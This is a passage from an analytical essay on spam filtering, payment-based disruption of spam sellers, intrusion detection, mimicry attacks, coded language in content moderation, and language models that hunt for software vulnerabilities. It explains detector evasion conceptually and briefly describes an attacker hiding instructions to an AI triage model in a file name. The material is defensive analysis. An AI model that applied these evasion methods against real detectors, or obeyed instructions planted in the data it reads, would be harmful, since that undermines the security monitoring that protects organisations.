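Lowd and Meek found that frequent retraining was the only effective defence against good-word attacks. Their strongest attacks reduced the amount of spam blocked by 87% for a naive Bayes filter and by more than 99% for a maximum entropy filter. They then retrained both filters on the original 500,000 messages and 5,000 newer ones, in which they had added good words to the spam, and gave the newer messages extra weight. Both filters again blocked about as much spam as before the attack, with or without the added words.

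The experiment did not include a spammer who responds by finding a new list of words. Lowd and Meek assume, and hope, that filters can be retrained faster than spammers can find new lists. Keeping the old messages in the training set should at least help prevent the cycle that Dalvi and colleagues observed, in which each new filter lost what had been learned in earlier rounds.

Retraining a spam filter only means counting words again once somebody has labelled the messages correctly, so it doesn't require an explanation of why an attack worked. But the labels usually come from people, who recognise a disguised advertisement because they understand what it offers. Users therefore supply some of the general cognition that the filter lacks, after the attack has arrived. Malware detectors get similar help from the analysts who examine new files.

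Relying on reports also lets attackers influence what the filter learns. Virus Bulletin describes an experiment in which a poisoned filter rated messages in general as more likely to be spam, and so blocked more legitimate mail. Users may also mislabel messages by accident or disagree about what spam is.

### The payment bottleneck

Levchenko and colleagues looked for a weakness in the spammers' business instead of in their messages. Between August and October 2010 they collected nearly a billion web addresses from spam. They traced the sites that sold drugs, counterfeit luxury goods and pirated software, and recorded who had registered the domains and who ran the servers. They also placed more than 100 orders to find out which banks received the money.

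Spammers could replace domains and servers quickly and cheaply, but banks were much harder to replace. Few banks would knowingly process payments for spam-advertised goods, and opening a new account took days or weeks. Three banks handled the payments for over 95% of the goods in the study. This estimate assumes that all the sites in one sales programme used the same bank, which the test purchases largely confirmed. The researchers suggested that American banks refuse certain card payments to banks on a list, which investigators could update faster than sellers could open new accounts.

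Sellers had little room to absorb extra costs. In a 2013 presentation, Savage, one of the researchers, put the sellers' profit margin at 16.3%, after direct costs of 70.8% and indirect costs of 12.8%.

Brand owners soon put the idea into practice by making test purchases and reporting the sellers' accounts to Visa and Mastercard. *Priceless* (McCoy, Dharmdasani and colleagues, 2012) tracked what happened after an account fell out of use. If the account had drawn a complaint, the next purchase from the same seller went through another bank in 69% of cases and failed in 21%. For accounts without complaints, the figures were about 45% and 18%. Complaints therefore seem to have forced sellers to switch banks more often than they stopped sales. But switching was expensive, because the old bank could keep the money it had held back against refunds, often more than a million dollars.

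The effect was strongest on sellers of pirated software. One brand owner pursued every new account in that market. After complaints about software sellers, 6 of the next 16 purchases failed, compared with 8 of 44 without complaints. The samples are small, but messages on the sellers' own forums also described programmes closing.

The sellers adapted too. Some disguised drug sales as groceries or cosmetics in the payment records, and others stopped selling the brands whose owners had complained. Several tried to screen out investigators by telephoning new customers or asking for identity documents. McCoy (2016) describes payment processors for counterfeit goods building filters to detect test purchases and sharing blacklists. The sellers and processors now had the defender's problem of catching a few disguised adversaries without turning away honest customers. After one drug seller began asking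 for photo identification, an affiliate complained that only about 10% of his orders were going through.

To find the bottleneck, people had to understand banking, advertising and crime, which is the kind of broad understanding premise 3 describes. But they did this work once, outside any filter. Investigators still had to keep making purchases and complaints, but they did not have to rediscover that sellers needed banks. When Levchenko and colleagues continued their purchases for four months after the study, only one new bank appeared.

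### When retraining is too late

A classifier can rely on retraining instead of predicting new attacks if an attacker has to repeat an attack many times to profit from it. Suppose a spammer spends $500 finding a new disguise and earns $100 an hour until the filter learns to block it. If the filter adapts within five hours, the spammer makes no profit. A large campaign also quickly produces the reports needed to retrain the filter.

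This advantage could shrink. By the same calculation, if automation cut the cost of a new disguise to $50, the filter would have to adapt within half an hour. In 2005, Lowd and Meek suggested that a spammer could use a language model to turn a list of good words into plausible sentences. A defender could try to keep up by generating likely attacks and training on them in advance, as developers do with large models, but would then have to do some of the anticipating that retraining was supposed to replace.

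Fast retraining matters less when a single success causes most of the damage. If malware goes to 10,000 companies and the first ten report it, an update may still protect the other 9,990. But if the attacker makes a sufficiently different version for each company, every company is in the same position as the first victim. EMBER2024's challenge files show that antivirus products eventually recognise malware they all initially missed, but this helps little once an attacker has encrypted a company's files for ransom. A spy who wants to open one particular person's mailbox may need only one attempt. In such cases the defence has to work the first time, so somebody must work out beforehand what an attacker could change and decide what a program that gets through will be able to reach.

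## Intrusion detection by signature, anomaly and specification

If an attack gets past a filter or malware detector, the defender can still try to detect the attacker inside the system. An intrusion detector is a program that monitors a computer's activity records, such as logins, opened files and network connections, and raises an alarm about anything that may be an attack.

There are three main types of intrusion detector, and each needs different knowledge in advance. A signature detector has a list of patterns from known attacks. An anomaly detector has a learned model of normal behaviour, an approach that Dorothy Denning set out in 1987. A specification-based detector has a written statement of what each program is allowed to do. Only the signature detector contains information about attackers, so if premise 3 is right, the other two should catch very little.

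### One intrusion, three detectors

Wagner and Soto (2002), in *Mimicry Attacks on Host-Based Intrusion Detection Systems*, give the example of a script that exploits a flaw in a mail program and takes control of it. The script adds an account to the computer's password file, so that the attacker can return, and starts a shell that waits for him to connect. To do this, the mail program makes nine system calls:

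open, write, close, socket, bind, listen, accept, read, fork

The first three change the password file. The next five wait for a connection and read from it, and the last starts a new process.

A signature detector will catch the script if someone has already analysed it and stored a recognisable piece of it. If the script exploits an unknown flaw, the detector probably has nothing to match. *Specification-based Detection for Unix Privileged Programs* (Ko, 1995) gives this as the reason for looking beyond signatures, since such flaws are often subtle and very hard to find. An attacker can also alter a known script slightly to evade the detector. Wagner and Soto consider this so easy that they leave signature detectors out of their study.

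Stephanie Forrest and colleagues at the University of New Mexico designed an anomaly detector that would probably catch the script on its first appearance. It first records a program's system calls while nobody is attacking, and stores every run of six consecutive calls in a database D. It then monitors the program's later calls s₁, s₂, s₃ and so on, and counts the runs that are missing from D:

number of positions i for which (sᵢ, sᵢ₊₁, …, sᵢ₊₅) ∉ D.

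The nine calls above contain four runs of six. A mail program is unlikely to change a file and then immediately wait for connections, so several of the four would be missing. The detector needs no information about password files or shells to notice this. But it might also raise an alarm if an honest update gave the mail program a new feature. (Lily, the check for backdoors, reduces this problem by comparing the new version with the old one.)

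In Ko's approach, a person writes down what a program should do, based on its function and the site's security policy, and a monitor reports any departure. A specification for the mail program might allow it to write only to mailboxes and its own temporary files. The script would break this rule with its first call, even if the script was new and its calls were ordinary. Ko's prototype monitored privileged Unix programs and immediately detected several known attacks. This is a fairer test than it would be for a signature detector, which would find known attacks easy, because Ko's specifications describe the programs' proper work rather than the attacks.

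An intruder who has stolen a password may evade both signature and specification detection. He logs in normally and reads files that the password's owner may read, so he uses no known attack and breaks no rule. An anomaly detector might still flag that the account is active at three in the morning, or that it is opening files its owner has never needed. Few other methods have any chance of detecting such an intruder, so it matters a great deal whether anomaly detectors are usable in practice.

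### Twenty records in a million

The main obstacle is false alarms. In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson imagined a site whose few dozen computers produce a million records a day. It has two intrusions a day, each affecting ten records, so 20 records in a million belong to intrusions.

Let I mean that a record belongs to an intrusion, and A that the detector raises an alarm about it. The detection rate is P(A | I) and the false alarm rate is P(A | not I). Bayes' theorem gives the probability that an alarm is right:

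P(I | A) = P(I) P(A | I) / [P(I) P(A | I) + P(not I) P(A | not I)].

Here P(I) is 20 in a million, or 0.00002. If the detector catches every intrusion and has a false alarm rate of 1 in 100,000, then

P(I | A) = 0.00002 / (0.00002 + 0.99998 × 0.00001) ≈ 0.67.

In a day, the detector flags all 20 intrusion records and about 10 of the 999,980 harmless ones, so about two thirds of its alarms are correct. The following table shows what happens when it misses more intrusions or flags more harmless records.

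| Detection rate | False alarm rate | Intrusion records flagged | Harmless records flagged | Share of alarms that are right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 100% | 1 in 100,000 | 20 | 10 | 67% |
| 70% | 1 in 100,000 | 14 | 10 | 58% |
| 100% | 1 in 10,000 | 20 | 100 | 17% |
| 100% | 1 in 1,000 | 20 | 1,000 | 2% |

Missing 30% of the intrusion records makes a detector's alarms only slightly less reliable, but a tenfold increase in the false alarm rate makes them almost useless, because harmless records outnumber intrusion records by about 50,000 to one. The same arithmetic applied to the malware detectors, although there one app in a hundred was malicious.

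If the detector groups the records in tens, as Axelsson also supposes, the last row of the table amounts to 2 correct alarms and 100 false ones a day. One person could perhaps investigate them all, but Axelsson doubts that anyone would keep doing so. He knew of no experiments with intrusion alarms, but research on the operators of power stations, paper mills and large ships suggests that most people have stopped trusting an alarm by the time half its warnings are false. An analyst who ignores the alarms will miss even the intrusions that the detector catches, so a detector that misses three intrusions in ten but keeps the analyst's trust is more useful.

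When Axelsson compared these requirements with published tests, the best signature detectors came close to a false alarm rate of 1 in 100,000. The anomaly detectors had rates at least ten times as high, though he had only one study of them. A signature describes something specific that honest users rarely do by chance, while an anomaly detector flags whatever is new, which includes much of what honest users do. However, the signature detectors' detection rates fell sharply on attacks they had no signatures for.

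One of Denning's models shows how difficult such a low rate is to guarantee. It flags a measurement, such as the number of files a user opens in an hour, if it is more than d standard deviations from that user's average. By Chebyshev's inequality, this happens at most 1/d² of the time, however the measurements are distributed. To guarantee at most one false alarm in 100,000, d would have to be about 316, and an intruder could open far more files than usual before reaching that limit. A much smaller d is usually enough in practice, but to choose it safely, the designers need to know about the rarest harmless behaviour, of which they have the fewest examples.

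The detection rate in Axelsson's calculation is an average, so an adaptive adversary can still look for an attack that raises no alarm. The adversary can also benefit from false alarms. Axelsson recalls old advice that an intruder should try to get past a burglar alarm during normal working hours, when the staff are used to false alarms and may ignore a real one.

### Unusual but harmless

Robin Sommer and Vern Paxson (2010), in *Outside the Closed World*, asked why so few organisations used machine learning to detect intrusions when it had worked well for tasks such as recommending products. One reason they gave was that errors do more harm in intrusion detection. A shop loses little if it recommends a book that the customer doesn't want, but every false alarm takes up an analyst's time, and a missed intrusion can do serious damage.

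The harm a false alarm does depends partly on how the detector responds. pH, a later detector based on Forrest's approach, alerts the administrator and also slows the suspicious program down. If m of the program's recent runs of six calls are missing from the database, pH delays its next call by 2ᵐ units of time. One missing run causes a delay of 2 units, which may go unnoticed, while 20 missing runs cause a delay of about a million units. The program can recover from a small false alarm without an analyst investigating.

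Sommer and Paxson also pointed out that unusual activity is not necessarily malicious. An anomaly detector may report that a computer sent 40 gigabytes to an unfamiliar address overnight. This could be data theft or the first run of a new backup service, and the analyst has to find out which.

Their other main reason was a lack of data. Records of real network traffic contain private information, so few organisations share them, and traffic that is normal on one network may be unusual on another. Researchers can simulate traffic instead, but the results may be misleading. The largest test that Axelsson discusses used simulated traffic to evaluate signature detectors, and he suspected that the harmless traffic hardly changed between training and testing. If so, a detector with too narrow a model of harmless traffic would have raised fewer false alarms in the test than in real use.

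A language model could help with triage by reading the alarms first and passing on only those that deserve an analyst's attention. It can explain what an unfamiliar command does, or compare a large transfer with a schedule of planned maintenance, which helps distinguish malicious activity from activity that is only unusual. Its training also covers ordinary software and common attacks, so it depends less on labelled examples from each network, which partly makes up for the lack of data.

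The problem of errors is harder to solve. Suppose a detector raises 2 correct alarms and 100 false ones a day, and a model passes on 95% of the correct alarms and dismisses 95% of the false ones. The analyst then receives, on average, 1.9 correct alarms and 5 false ones a day, so about 28% are right instead of 2%. For about two thirds to be right, the model would have to dismiss 99% of the false alarms. It would also have to do this when an attacker writes some of what it reads, including commands and file names. The attacker can give a theft the name of a backup job, or hide instructions to the model in a file name. The model would therefore pass on fewer real intrusions than tests on ordinary alarms suggest.

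Triage does seem to need broad understanding, but much of it is about the company rather than attackers. To interpret the 40-gigabyte transfer, the analyst or the model needs information about what the company has bought, who is working late and which old systems behave oddly. In this case, the breadth comes more from the variety of honest behaviour than from the variety of attacks that premise 5 relies on.

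### Attacks that imitate normal behaviour

An attacker who knows what an anomaly detector counts as normal can try to stay within it. Wagner and Soto call this a mimicry attack. Let N be the set of all sequences of system calls that the detector accepts, and M the set of sequences that would do the harm the attacker wants. Once he has control of a program, he can do this harm without an alarm if

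N ∩ M ≠ ∅,

that is, if at least one sequence is in both sets. Taking control often requires no system calls, so the detector has nothing to flag until the attacker starts to use the program.

M can be very large, because many different sequences do the same harm. The attacker can change the order of some calls, add others that have no useful effect, or wait until the program would normally do something similar. At the time, almost all detectors of this kind recorded only that a program had opened a file, not which file, so opening the password file looked the same as opening any other.

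Wagner and Soto tried this idea on pH, using a published attack on a file-transfer server that pH detected in its original form. They wrote a program that searches for a sequence in both N and M in less than a second, and it found no way to disguise the original attack. They then changed some of the steps by hand, so that the attack added an account to the password file instead of opening a shell. After a few hours of work with the search program, they found a version in which every run of six calls was in pH's database. The few harmful calls were spread among more than a hundred others.

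They did not run this version against a protected computer, but they used a separate program to confirm that the database would accept the sequence. They tested only one attack on one server, and assumed that an attacker could predict most of the database by studying other computers with the same software. The experiment therefore shows that mimicry is possible, but not how often it would work.

The search was a narrow computation, but the researchers needed broader understanding to see that a new account would serve an intruder as well as a shell would. A defender could run the same search before deploying a detector, to find which kinds of harm it would miss. But someone would first have to describe each kind of harm, and might not think of the substitute that the attacker chooses.

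Mimicry becomes harder when the detector models normal behaviour in more detail. Wagner and Soto recommend checking the details of each call, such as which file it opens, and whether the call fails. Later detectors learned which details were normal, so an attacker could no longer just open the password file in place of another one. Other detectors checked where in the program each call came from, though researchers then found mimicry attacks on one of them. An attacker may need considerably more skill and time to evade such a detector, even if he can still do it.

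A finer model also makes N smaller, so more legitimate behaviour falls outside it. If the additional checks raised the false alarm rate from 1 in 100,000 to 1 in 10,000, the share of alarms that are correct would fall from 67% to 17% at Axelsson's site. Designers therefore have to choose between a strict model that exhausts the analyst with false alarms and a loose one that attackers can evade by mimicking normal behaviour.

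A detector can avoid the false alarms by using a specification derived from the program's own code. Software analyses the code before it runs and works out every sequence of calls it could make. The program makes only these sequences unless it is attacked, so a detector that accepts them all raises no false alarms. But an attacker can use any of them too, including some that the program would hardly ever produce. If a mail program's code can write to any file, for example, the derived specification may allow it to change the password file. A person who knows what the mail program is for can write a stricter rule.

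### Files that nobody should open

Decoys avoid much of this trade-off. A decoy is a file, account or password that no honest user has a reason to touch. A company might leave a password for a nonexistent database on an employee's laptop. If anyone tries to use it, somebody has probably been searching the laptop. The defender doesn't need to know how the intruder got in, and an intruder who imitates the employee's normal behaviour can still be detected if he uses the decoy.

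Alarms from decoys can be reliable even if decoys catch few intruders. Suppose Axelsson's site has 200 intrusions in 100 days, decoys expose 10% of them, and an employee touches a decoy by accident once. Then 20 of the 21 alarms, or about 95%, are correct. The decoys miss the other 180 intrusions, so they can only supplement other detectors. The site would also have to exempt backup programs and virus scanners, which open nearly every file, and an intruder who controlled one of these could read the decoys without raising an alarm.

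A decoy works better if it appeals to the intruder. In the 1980s, Clifford Stoll, who managed computers at the Lawrence Berkeley Laboratory in California, watched an intruder search for military information. Stoll and his colleagues created fake files about a missile-defence network, and the intruder spent long enough on them for the telephone companies to finish tracing his call to Hanover. Stoll had worked out what this intruder wanted, as premise 3 would suggest, but the files needed no intelligence of their own. Simpler decoys require only the guess that most intruders want passwords. A spy who already knows which file he wants may never touch a decoy, and a careful intruder may become suspicious of an account that nobody has ever used.

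### The work left to people

None of these detectors has to represent an attacker's goal while it runs. A signature represents only a part of an attack that somebody has already seen. After each new attack, an analyst has to work out what happened and write another signature, and the first victims get no protection. Signature detection therefore avoids premise 3 only because people analyze the new attacks.

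An analyst, or a language model doing triage, has to decide what each alarm from an anomaly detector means. This work never ends, because honest users keep doing new things. If the decision depends on why someone might want certain files, the analyst or model has to do the modelling of motives that the detector didn't need.

Specifications come closest to avoiding premise 3, because most of the work happens before the program runs and concerns the program rather than its attackers. Developers can sometimes prove in advance that a program meets its specification. But someone still has to write the rules, revise them when the program changes and consider how an attacker might misuse what they permit. That is feasible for a few programs with special privileges, but much harder for everything that people do on an office network.

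Rules of this kind help least when the same action can be honest or dishonest. A payroll clerk copying the salary list for an auditor may open the same file, at the same time of day, as one copying it for a competitor. A rule could stop the clerk from copying the list, but then the auditor would not get it. To allow one copy and block the other, somebody has to find out what the clerk intends to do with it.

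## Content moderation against coded language and changing memes

Content moderation, the work of deciding which posts a platform should remove, is one of the best cases for the view that defence needs general cognition. What a post means depends on what its readers understand, so a rule against hateful posts is harder to write than a rule about the payroll clerk's file, which is the same file each time.

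Platforms have written rules. *The Hateful Memes Challenge* (Kiela, Firooz and colleagues, 2020) uses a definition close to Facebook's, in which hate speech is a direct or indirect attack on people because of characteristics such as race, religion or disability. Attacking a terrorist group is allowed, but equating the group with a race is not. The rule is short and could stay the same for years, but a moderator applying it must know which groups are terrorist groups and recognise an indirect attack. As with email, platforms cannot refuse content by default.

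### Codes, puns and second meanings

The simplest evasions change how a word looks. Writers replace letters with symbols, or whole words with emoji, to get a post past a filter while keeping it readable to people. Researchers call this algospeak. Other writers use an ordinary word in place of a forbidden one, such as "ice" for methamphetamine or "pot" for marijuana. A filter that banned "pot" would also remove posts about cooking.

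Chinese offers many more possibilities for coded language, because so many of its words sound alike. *How We Express Ourselves Freely* (2022) lists 14 ways users of the Chinese platform Weibo avoid censorship. For example, they write homophones or initials, rotate pictures of text, or publish something harmless and put the real message in a comment. Surveyed users thought satire, acronyms and homophones worked best.

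*Lost in Pronunciation* (2025) gives the example of a post that calls someone 64.5 grams of gold with a full price of 40,000. In Chinese, "full price 40,000" sounds like "whole family dead". But "I'm not Miss Li" is a harmless pun on "I don't understand", so a platform can't treat every pun as an insult.

Dog whistles, expressions with a second meaning for insiders, are harder to notice because nothing about them looks odd. *From Dogwhistles to Bullhorns* (Mendelsohn, Le Bras and colleagues, 2023) discusses the sentence "we need to end the cosmopolitan experiment". Most readers take "cosmopolitan" to mean "worldly", but a few know that it means "Jewish". The writer can deny the second meaning, much as an underhanded programmer can call a backdoor a mistake. Automatic toxicity detectors missed harmful posts that used such expressions, and the language model GPT-3 recognised some kinds much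 better than others. *Silent Signals, Loud Impact* (2024) collected examples from Reddit and the records of the US Congress to help models separate coded from ordinary uses of the same word.

Many people who use codes are not hostile. According to *Black Content Creators' Responses and Resistance Strategies on TikTok* (2023), creators use algospeak to get around moderation they consider excessive. Wan, Li and Huang (2026), in *“Newspaper Eat” Means “Not Tasty”*, studied Chinese-speaking customers who hide complaints in friendly-looking restaurant reviews. "Newspaper eat" translates two syllables that, when said quickly, sound like the Chinese for "not tasty". A moderator who finds a code therefore still has to work out what it says.

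### How codes spread and wear out

In 2016, users of the message board 4chan began writing the names of technology companies, including Google, in place of slurs, and no platform could ban the word "Google". Months later, by March 2017, *Detecting the Hate Code on Social Media* (2017) had described this kind of code, in which harmless, unrelated words stand for targeted groups, and proposed a way to detect it.

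When a platform bans a term, its users often replace it. *Zeitgeist-Aware Multimodal (ZAM) Datasets of Pro-Eating Disorder Short-Form Videos* (2026) describes how people who promote eating disorders respelled banned words with symbols. They also used pictures, which a list of banned words can't catch, such as deer to represent frailty. Korean pop stars were less common in these videos before the early 2020s, so a detector trained on older videos would have had few examples connecting them with eating disorders.

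Coded posts can stay up for reasons other than moderators failing to understand them. *Malicious earworms and useful memes* (2025) studied far-right use of popular sounds on TikTok and found that few hateful videos disappeared, even when the hate was explicit in the sound or text. Those explicit videos needed no decoding, and the study points to TikTok's reliance on users to report hateful videos.

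Codes also hinder the people who use them, because every change makes a message harder to read. Fillies, Robertson and Hancock (2026), in *Algospeak, Hiding in the Open*, measured this with 20 false statements about COVID-19. They disguised each statement in seven ways and at five strengths, which gave 700 versions, and tested seven language models on them. With GPT-4o-mini as the detector, hiding half the statements took an average of 2.7 code words or 4.4 paraphrased words. The model still caught over 80% of the statements disguised with one kind of respelling, even at the greatest strength.

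The researchers also asked the models to recover the original words. GPT-4o-mini succeeded only 40% of the time when a statement contained a single unfamiliar code word. No human readers took part, but people who already shared a code would do much better. A code therefore helps only if its audience knows something the detector does not. To reach a wide public, users have to keep teaching the code to newcomers, and a detector can learn from the same posts.

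### A picture and its caption

A meme can be hateful even if its picture and caption are each harmless on their own. Kiela and colleagues give the example of a picture of a tumbleweed captioned "look how many people love you", which is cruel. Replacing the tumbleweed with a crowd makes the meme kind, and keeping the tumbleweed but changing "love" to "hate" makes it harmless. Making both changes makes it cruel again.

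No filter that scores the caption and the picture separately and adds the results, as a simple spam filter does with words, can get all four right. Let t be the score of a caption, v the score of a picture and θ the threshold for blocking. To block the two cruel memes, the filter needs

t(love) + v(tumbleweed) > θ and t(hate) + v(crowd) > θ,

so the four scores must add up to more than 2θ. To allow the two harmless ones, it needs

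t(love) + v(crowd) ≤ θ and t(hate) + v(tumbleweed) ≤ θ,

so the same four scores must add up to no more than 2θ. The filter has to consider the picture and caption together.

Kiela and colleagues built a set of 10,000 memes around this difficulty. Where they could, they paired each hateful meme with harmless versions that had a different picture or caption. Half of the test memes were hateful, so guessing would get 50% right. The best model in 2020 got 69.5% right and a model that read only the text got 62.8%, while trained annotators got 84.7%. In the competition that followed, which used new test memes, the system described in *Detecting Hate Speech in Memes Using Multimodal Deep Learning Approaches* (Velioglu and Rose, 2020) got 76.5% right and came third out of 3,173 participants.

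That gap has since nearly closed. In *Learn Before You Judge*, Xu, Wang and colleagues (2026) started with Qwen2.5-VL-7B, a fairly small model that handles both images and text. Without special training, it got 63.4% of the memes right. Training it on labelled memes raised this to 75.6%, and teaching it background knowledge before that training, such as what a historical event or symbol means, raised it to 81.9%. Extra training on the memes it was least sure about brought it to 83.5%. The annotators scored 84.7%, but the test memes may not be exactly the same. A method that used a model about ten times as large, without training it for the task, got 75.8%.

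Smaller specialised programs can do well too. In *Small Cues, Big Consequences*, Sharma and Patil (2026) built a classifier that correctly labelled 88% of a set of COVID-19 memes, and they report that trained classifiers still outperform leading general models on that set. But when they trained their classifier on memes about LGBTQ+ people, its accuracy fell from 77% on new memes from the same set to 61% on the Hateful Memes set.

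Narrow training therefore seems enough for a fixed collection of memes, but the skill transfers poorly to other subjects. Nobody was changing the memes in response to these classifiers, so the figures do not show how well the classifiers would do against an adaptive adversary.

### Finding codes that nobody has listed

A program can look for new codes without understanding why people use them. Zhu, Gong and colleagues (2021), in *Self-Supervised Euphemism Detection and Identification for Content Moderation*, start from a list of plain terms, such as the names of drugs. Their program works as follows:

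1. It collects sentences that contain a term such as "heroin" and hides the term.
2. It discards sentences that reveal little about the missing word. "Why is it so hard to find ___?" could be about almost anything, while a sentence about overdoses is more useful.
3. It asks a language model which words would fit the gaps in the remaining sentences, and ranks the answers.

One program ranks words highly if they appear where drug names appear, as "ice" does when dealers discuss its purity. At best, 40 to 45% of its top 20 suggestions were right, and some of the correct ones were missing from the researchers' own lists. A second program then works out which drug each word means, but neither program represents what a dealer wants.

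In *Using LLMs to discover emerging coded antisemitic hate-speech in extremist social media*, Kikkisetti, Mustafa and colleagues (2024) also start from known expressions. They collect posts containing them, find and count the phrases most typical of each post, and remove phrases that are openly about Jewish topics. The remaining phrases are possible codes.

Such methods do much worse when codes are rare. In *Making FETCH! Happen*, Sasse, Aguirre and colleagues (2024) gave several programs a fifth of the known dog whistles in a collection of posts and had them find the rest. Scores, out of 100, combined the share of suggestions that were right with the share of dog whistles found, giving more weight to the first. On Reddit posts that all contained a dog whistle, the best method based on word similarity scored 5.9, and a new method combining search with a language model scored 23.3. On a more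 realistic collection of 7 million tweets, the best scores were 2.5 and 4.6 respectively.

One version of the new method found 60% of the dog whistles in the tweets, but a person would have to check about 106 of its suggestions to find one real dog whistle. The programs also missed every emoji code and had trouble with newer terms such as "jogger", a racist code word from 2020. The language models in this test were small, and a current one would probably do better.

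Recognising codes in individual posts has the same base-rate problem as detecting intrusions. Wan and colleagues checked 5,391 ordinary restaurant reviews by hand and found coded language in only 19, or 0.35%. They then built a collection of 7,744 reviews, 900 of them coded. Gemini 2.5 Flash found 92% of the coded reviews, and 67% of the reviews it flagged were coded. If these figures cover the whole collection, it wrongly flagged about 6% of the uncoded reviews. At that rate, it would correctly flag about 32 of 10,000 ordinary reviews and wrongly flag about 600. The false-alarm figure may be too high, since some uncoded reviews were included in the collection because they looked coded.

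### Reading the policy along with the post

Older classifiers learned a platform's rules only through labelled examples, so a new rule meant new labels and more training. A language model can instead read the written policy each time it judges a post. In *Scaling Reinforcement Learning for Content Moderation with Large Language Models* (2025), the model receives a prompt q that contains instructions, the policy, the post and the name of the account. It gives its reasoning, a verdict and an estimate of

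P(y = 1 | q),

where y = 1 means that the post breaks the policy. The platform acts if this probability is above a threshold.

*Benchmarking System One Models in Online Moderation* (2026) tests models that are given the full moderation policy, and *Can Foundation Models Moderate Online Content?* (2026) compares written instructions with examples of past decisions as guidance for models. In *Safeguarding Decentralized Social Media* (2024), six openly available models judged posts against the rules of different online communities, and experts who reviewed the verdicts found them close to their own.

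A policy that forbids insults against a religious group can't list the words that people will use for that group next month. *It is not enough to give your moderation rules to ChatGPT* (2026) argues that moderation also needs discussion, appeals and an understanding of a community's values, and that people must supply these because AI "can only look backward". But people also learn coded terms from past use, and a model that can search recent posts doesn't have to rely on old training data. The argument is stronger for values, because a community may want to change its rules, and its past decisions can't show what it will choose.

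### Signals that ignore the content

Some moderation methods don't interpret what a post means. In file matching, a platform stores a numerical fingerprint of each picture or video that people have judged forbidden, and compares new uploads with the list. The fingerprint has to stay nearly the same when someone resizes the picture or changes its colours slightly. Microsoft and Hany Farid, a computer scientist then at Dartmouth College, developed a system of this kind, PhotoDNA, in 2009 to find known images of child abuse. These images are illegal whatever the caption, so the program doesn't have to interpret them.

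File matching misses anything new. In March 2019, a gunman broadcast his attack on mosques in Christchurch, New Zealand, live on Facebook, and the broadcast matched nothing on any list. Facebook said it removed 1.5 million copies of the video in the next 24 hours, 1.2 million of them during upload. The other 300,000 were posted before Facebook removed them. People had cropped the video or filmed it from a screen, and Facebook counted more than 800 visibly different versions. Matching can also block a news report that includes part of a forbidden video.

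A platform can also look at how an account behaves. An hour-old account that has messaged 500 strangers is probably sending spam, whatever language it uses. But this doesn't help detect a real person who has used the same account for years and posts one hateful joke a week.

The timing of posts may reveal that one person controls a group of accounts. Suppose two unrelated people both share a link at random times on the same day. The chance that they do so within ten seconds of each other is 20/86,400, or about 1 in 4,300. The chance that this happens for each of five links is less than 1 in 10¹⁸. But real people do not post at random times. Thousands of football fans may post about the same goal within seconds, and honest campaigners may agree to post together. The person running the accounts can also add delays. Even a correct alarm shows only that the accounts work together, not that their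 message is harmful.

Limits on how far posts can spread apply to every post and require no detection. WhatsApp cannot read its users' encrypted messages, but in April 2020 it stopped people from forwarding a message to more than one chat at a time if it had already been forwarded many times. The company said that forwarding of these messages fell by 70%. If each person who receives a rumour passes it on to r others on average, and r is below 1, the rumour reaches about 1/(1 − r) people for each person who starts it, or five people when r is 0.8. But the limit slows useful warnings as much as rumours, and it doesn't protect someone who receives a threat meant only for them.

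These methods need an attacker model mainly at design time, when someone works out that spammers need many recipients or that propagandists reuse accounts. They are good at detecting repetition and scale, but they can't be used to determine whether a new post from an ordinary account is hateful.

### Knowing a culture and predicting an opponent

Judging such a post requires knowledge of a culture at a particular moment, which is different from predicting what an opponent will do next. A moderator who knows the pun about gold can remove the post without knowing what its author plans to do. The background knowledge that helped Xu and colleagues' model also covered events, public figures and symbols, but not how people evade moderation.

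Detecting dog whistles requires something closer to premise 3. The same complaint about "the cosmopolitan experiment" may come from an antisemite or from someone who just dislikes big cities. The moderator has to judge what the author wanted readers to understand, as people do when they recognise sarcasm, perhaps using the author's other posts and the replies. This requires modelling the author's intentions, but only what the author means, not how the author plans to defeat the filter.

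Predicting new codes would be more ambitious than learning them quickly once they appear, and probably less useful. Almost any word can become a code, as "Google" did, and a new code reaches few people until others have learned it, so a platform can usually wait for it to appear. The exception is a code that needs only one reader, such as a word that a drug dealer and a customer have agreed on in private.

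Moderation therefore gives premise 5 more support than the earlier cases. The knowledge it needs ranges from Chinese pronunciation to Korean pop music, and nobody can list it all in advance. Working out a new pun also takes some reasoning. But little of this work involves planning against an opponent, and much of it becomes a lookup once somebody has explained the code.

### Superhuman speed without deeper insight

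Human moderators also sometimes fail at this work. After four hours of training, Kiela and colleagues' annotators still disagreed with about 15% of the final labels. Zhu and colleagues note that moderators can usually tell when a word is a code but may not know what it means. For example, a moderator who reads no Chinese is unlikely to understand "newspaper eat".

A program could moderate better than people just by learning codes sooner and in more languages. Suppose a new code appears in 100 posts on its first day and its use doubles every two days. It will appear in 3,200 posts a day after ten days and 102,400 after 20. A program that learned the code in ten days, when human moderators needed 20, would prevent much harm without understanding people any better than the moderators do. It would also force users to replace codes before most of their readers had learned them.

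As with spam filters, though, false reports can corrupt what a program learns from its users. A group could report an innocent word as code to get its opponents' posts removed, so somebody has to check what the program learns, which takes time.

It is also unclear what superhuman accuracy would mean here. The correct label for a hateful meme is mostly whatever the majority of annotators chose, with experts settling the worst disagreements. A model could predict that label better than any single annotator, but there is no further fact about the meme to discover. When a community is divided over whether a joke is hateful, understanding all of the joke's coded language will not resolve the disagreement.

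## Language models that find software vulnerabilities

A machine can check much of what a language model claims about a program, such as that a given file will crash it. This makes the search for software flaws a good test of these models. In 2026 they found vulnerabilities that human reviewers and automatic tools had missed for decades. These models also write essays and answer medical questions, so if any automated reviewer succeeds because of general cognition, it should be one of them.

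### From a guess to a crash

Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities*, describe how Anthropic's researchers search a program. They put the program and its source code on an isolated system with no internet connection, and ask the model in a short paragraph to find a security flaw. The model can read files, run commands and use debugging tools. A typical search goes like this:

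1. The model reads some code and guesses at an assumption that may not always hold, for example that a message is never longer than the space set aside for it.
2. It follows the data through the program to see whether an outsider could supply a value that breaks the assumption.
3. It runs the program on such a value, and adds debugging output if the result is unclear.
4. If nothing goes wrong, it revises the guess or moves on. If the program fails, it writes a report that includes the input, so that other people can repeat the test.

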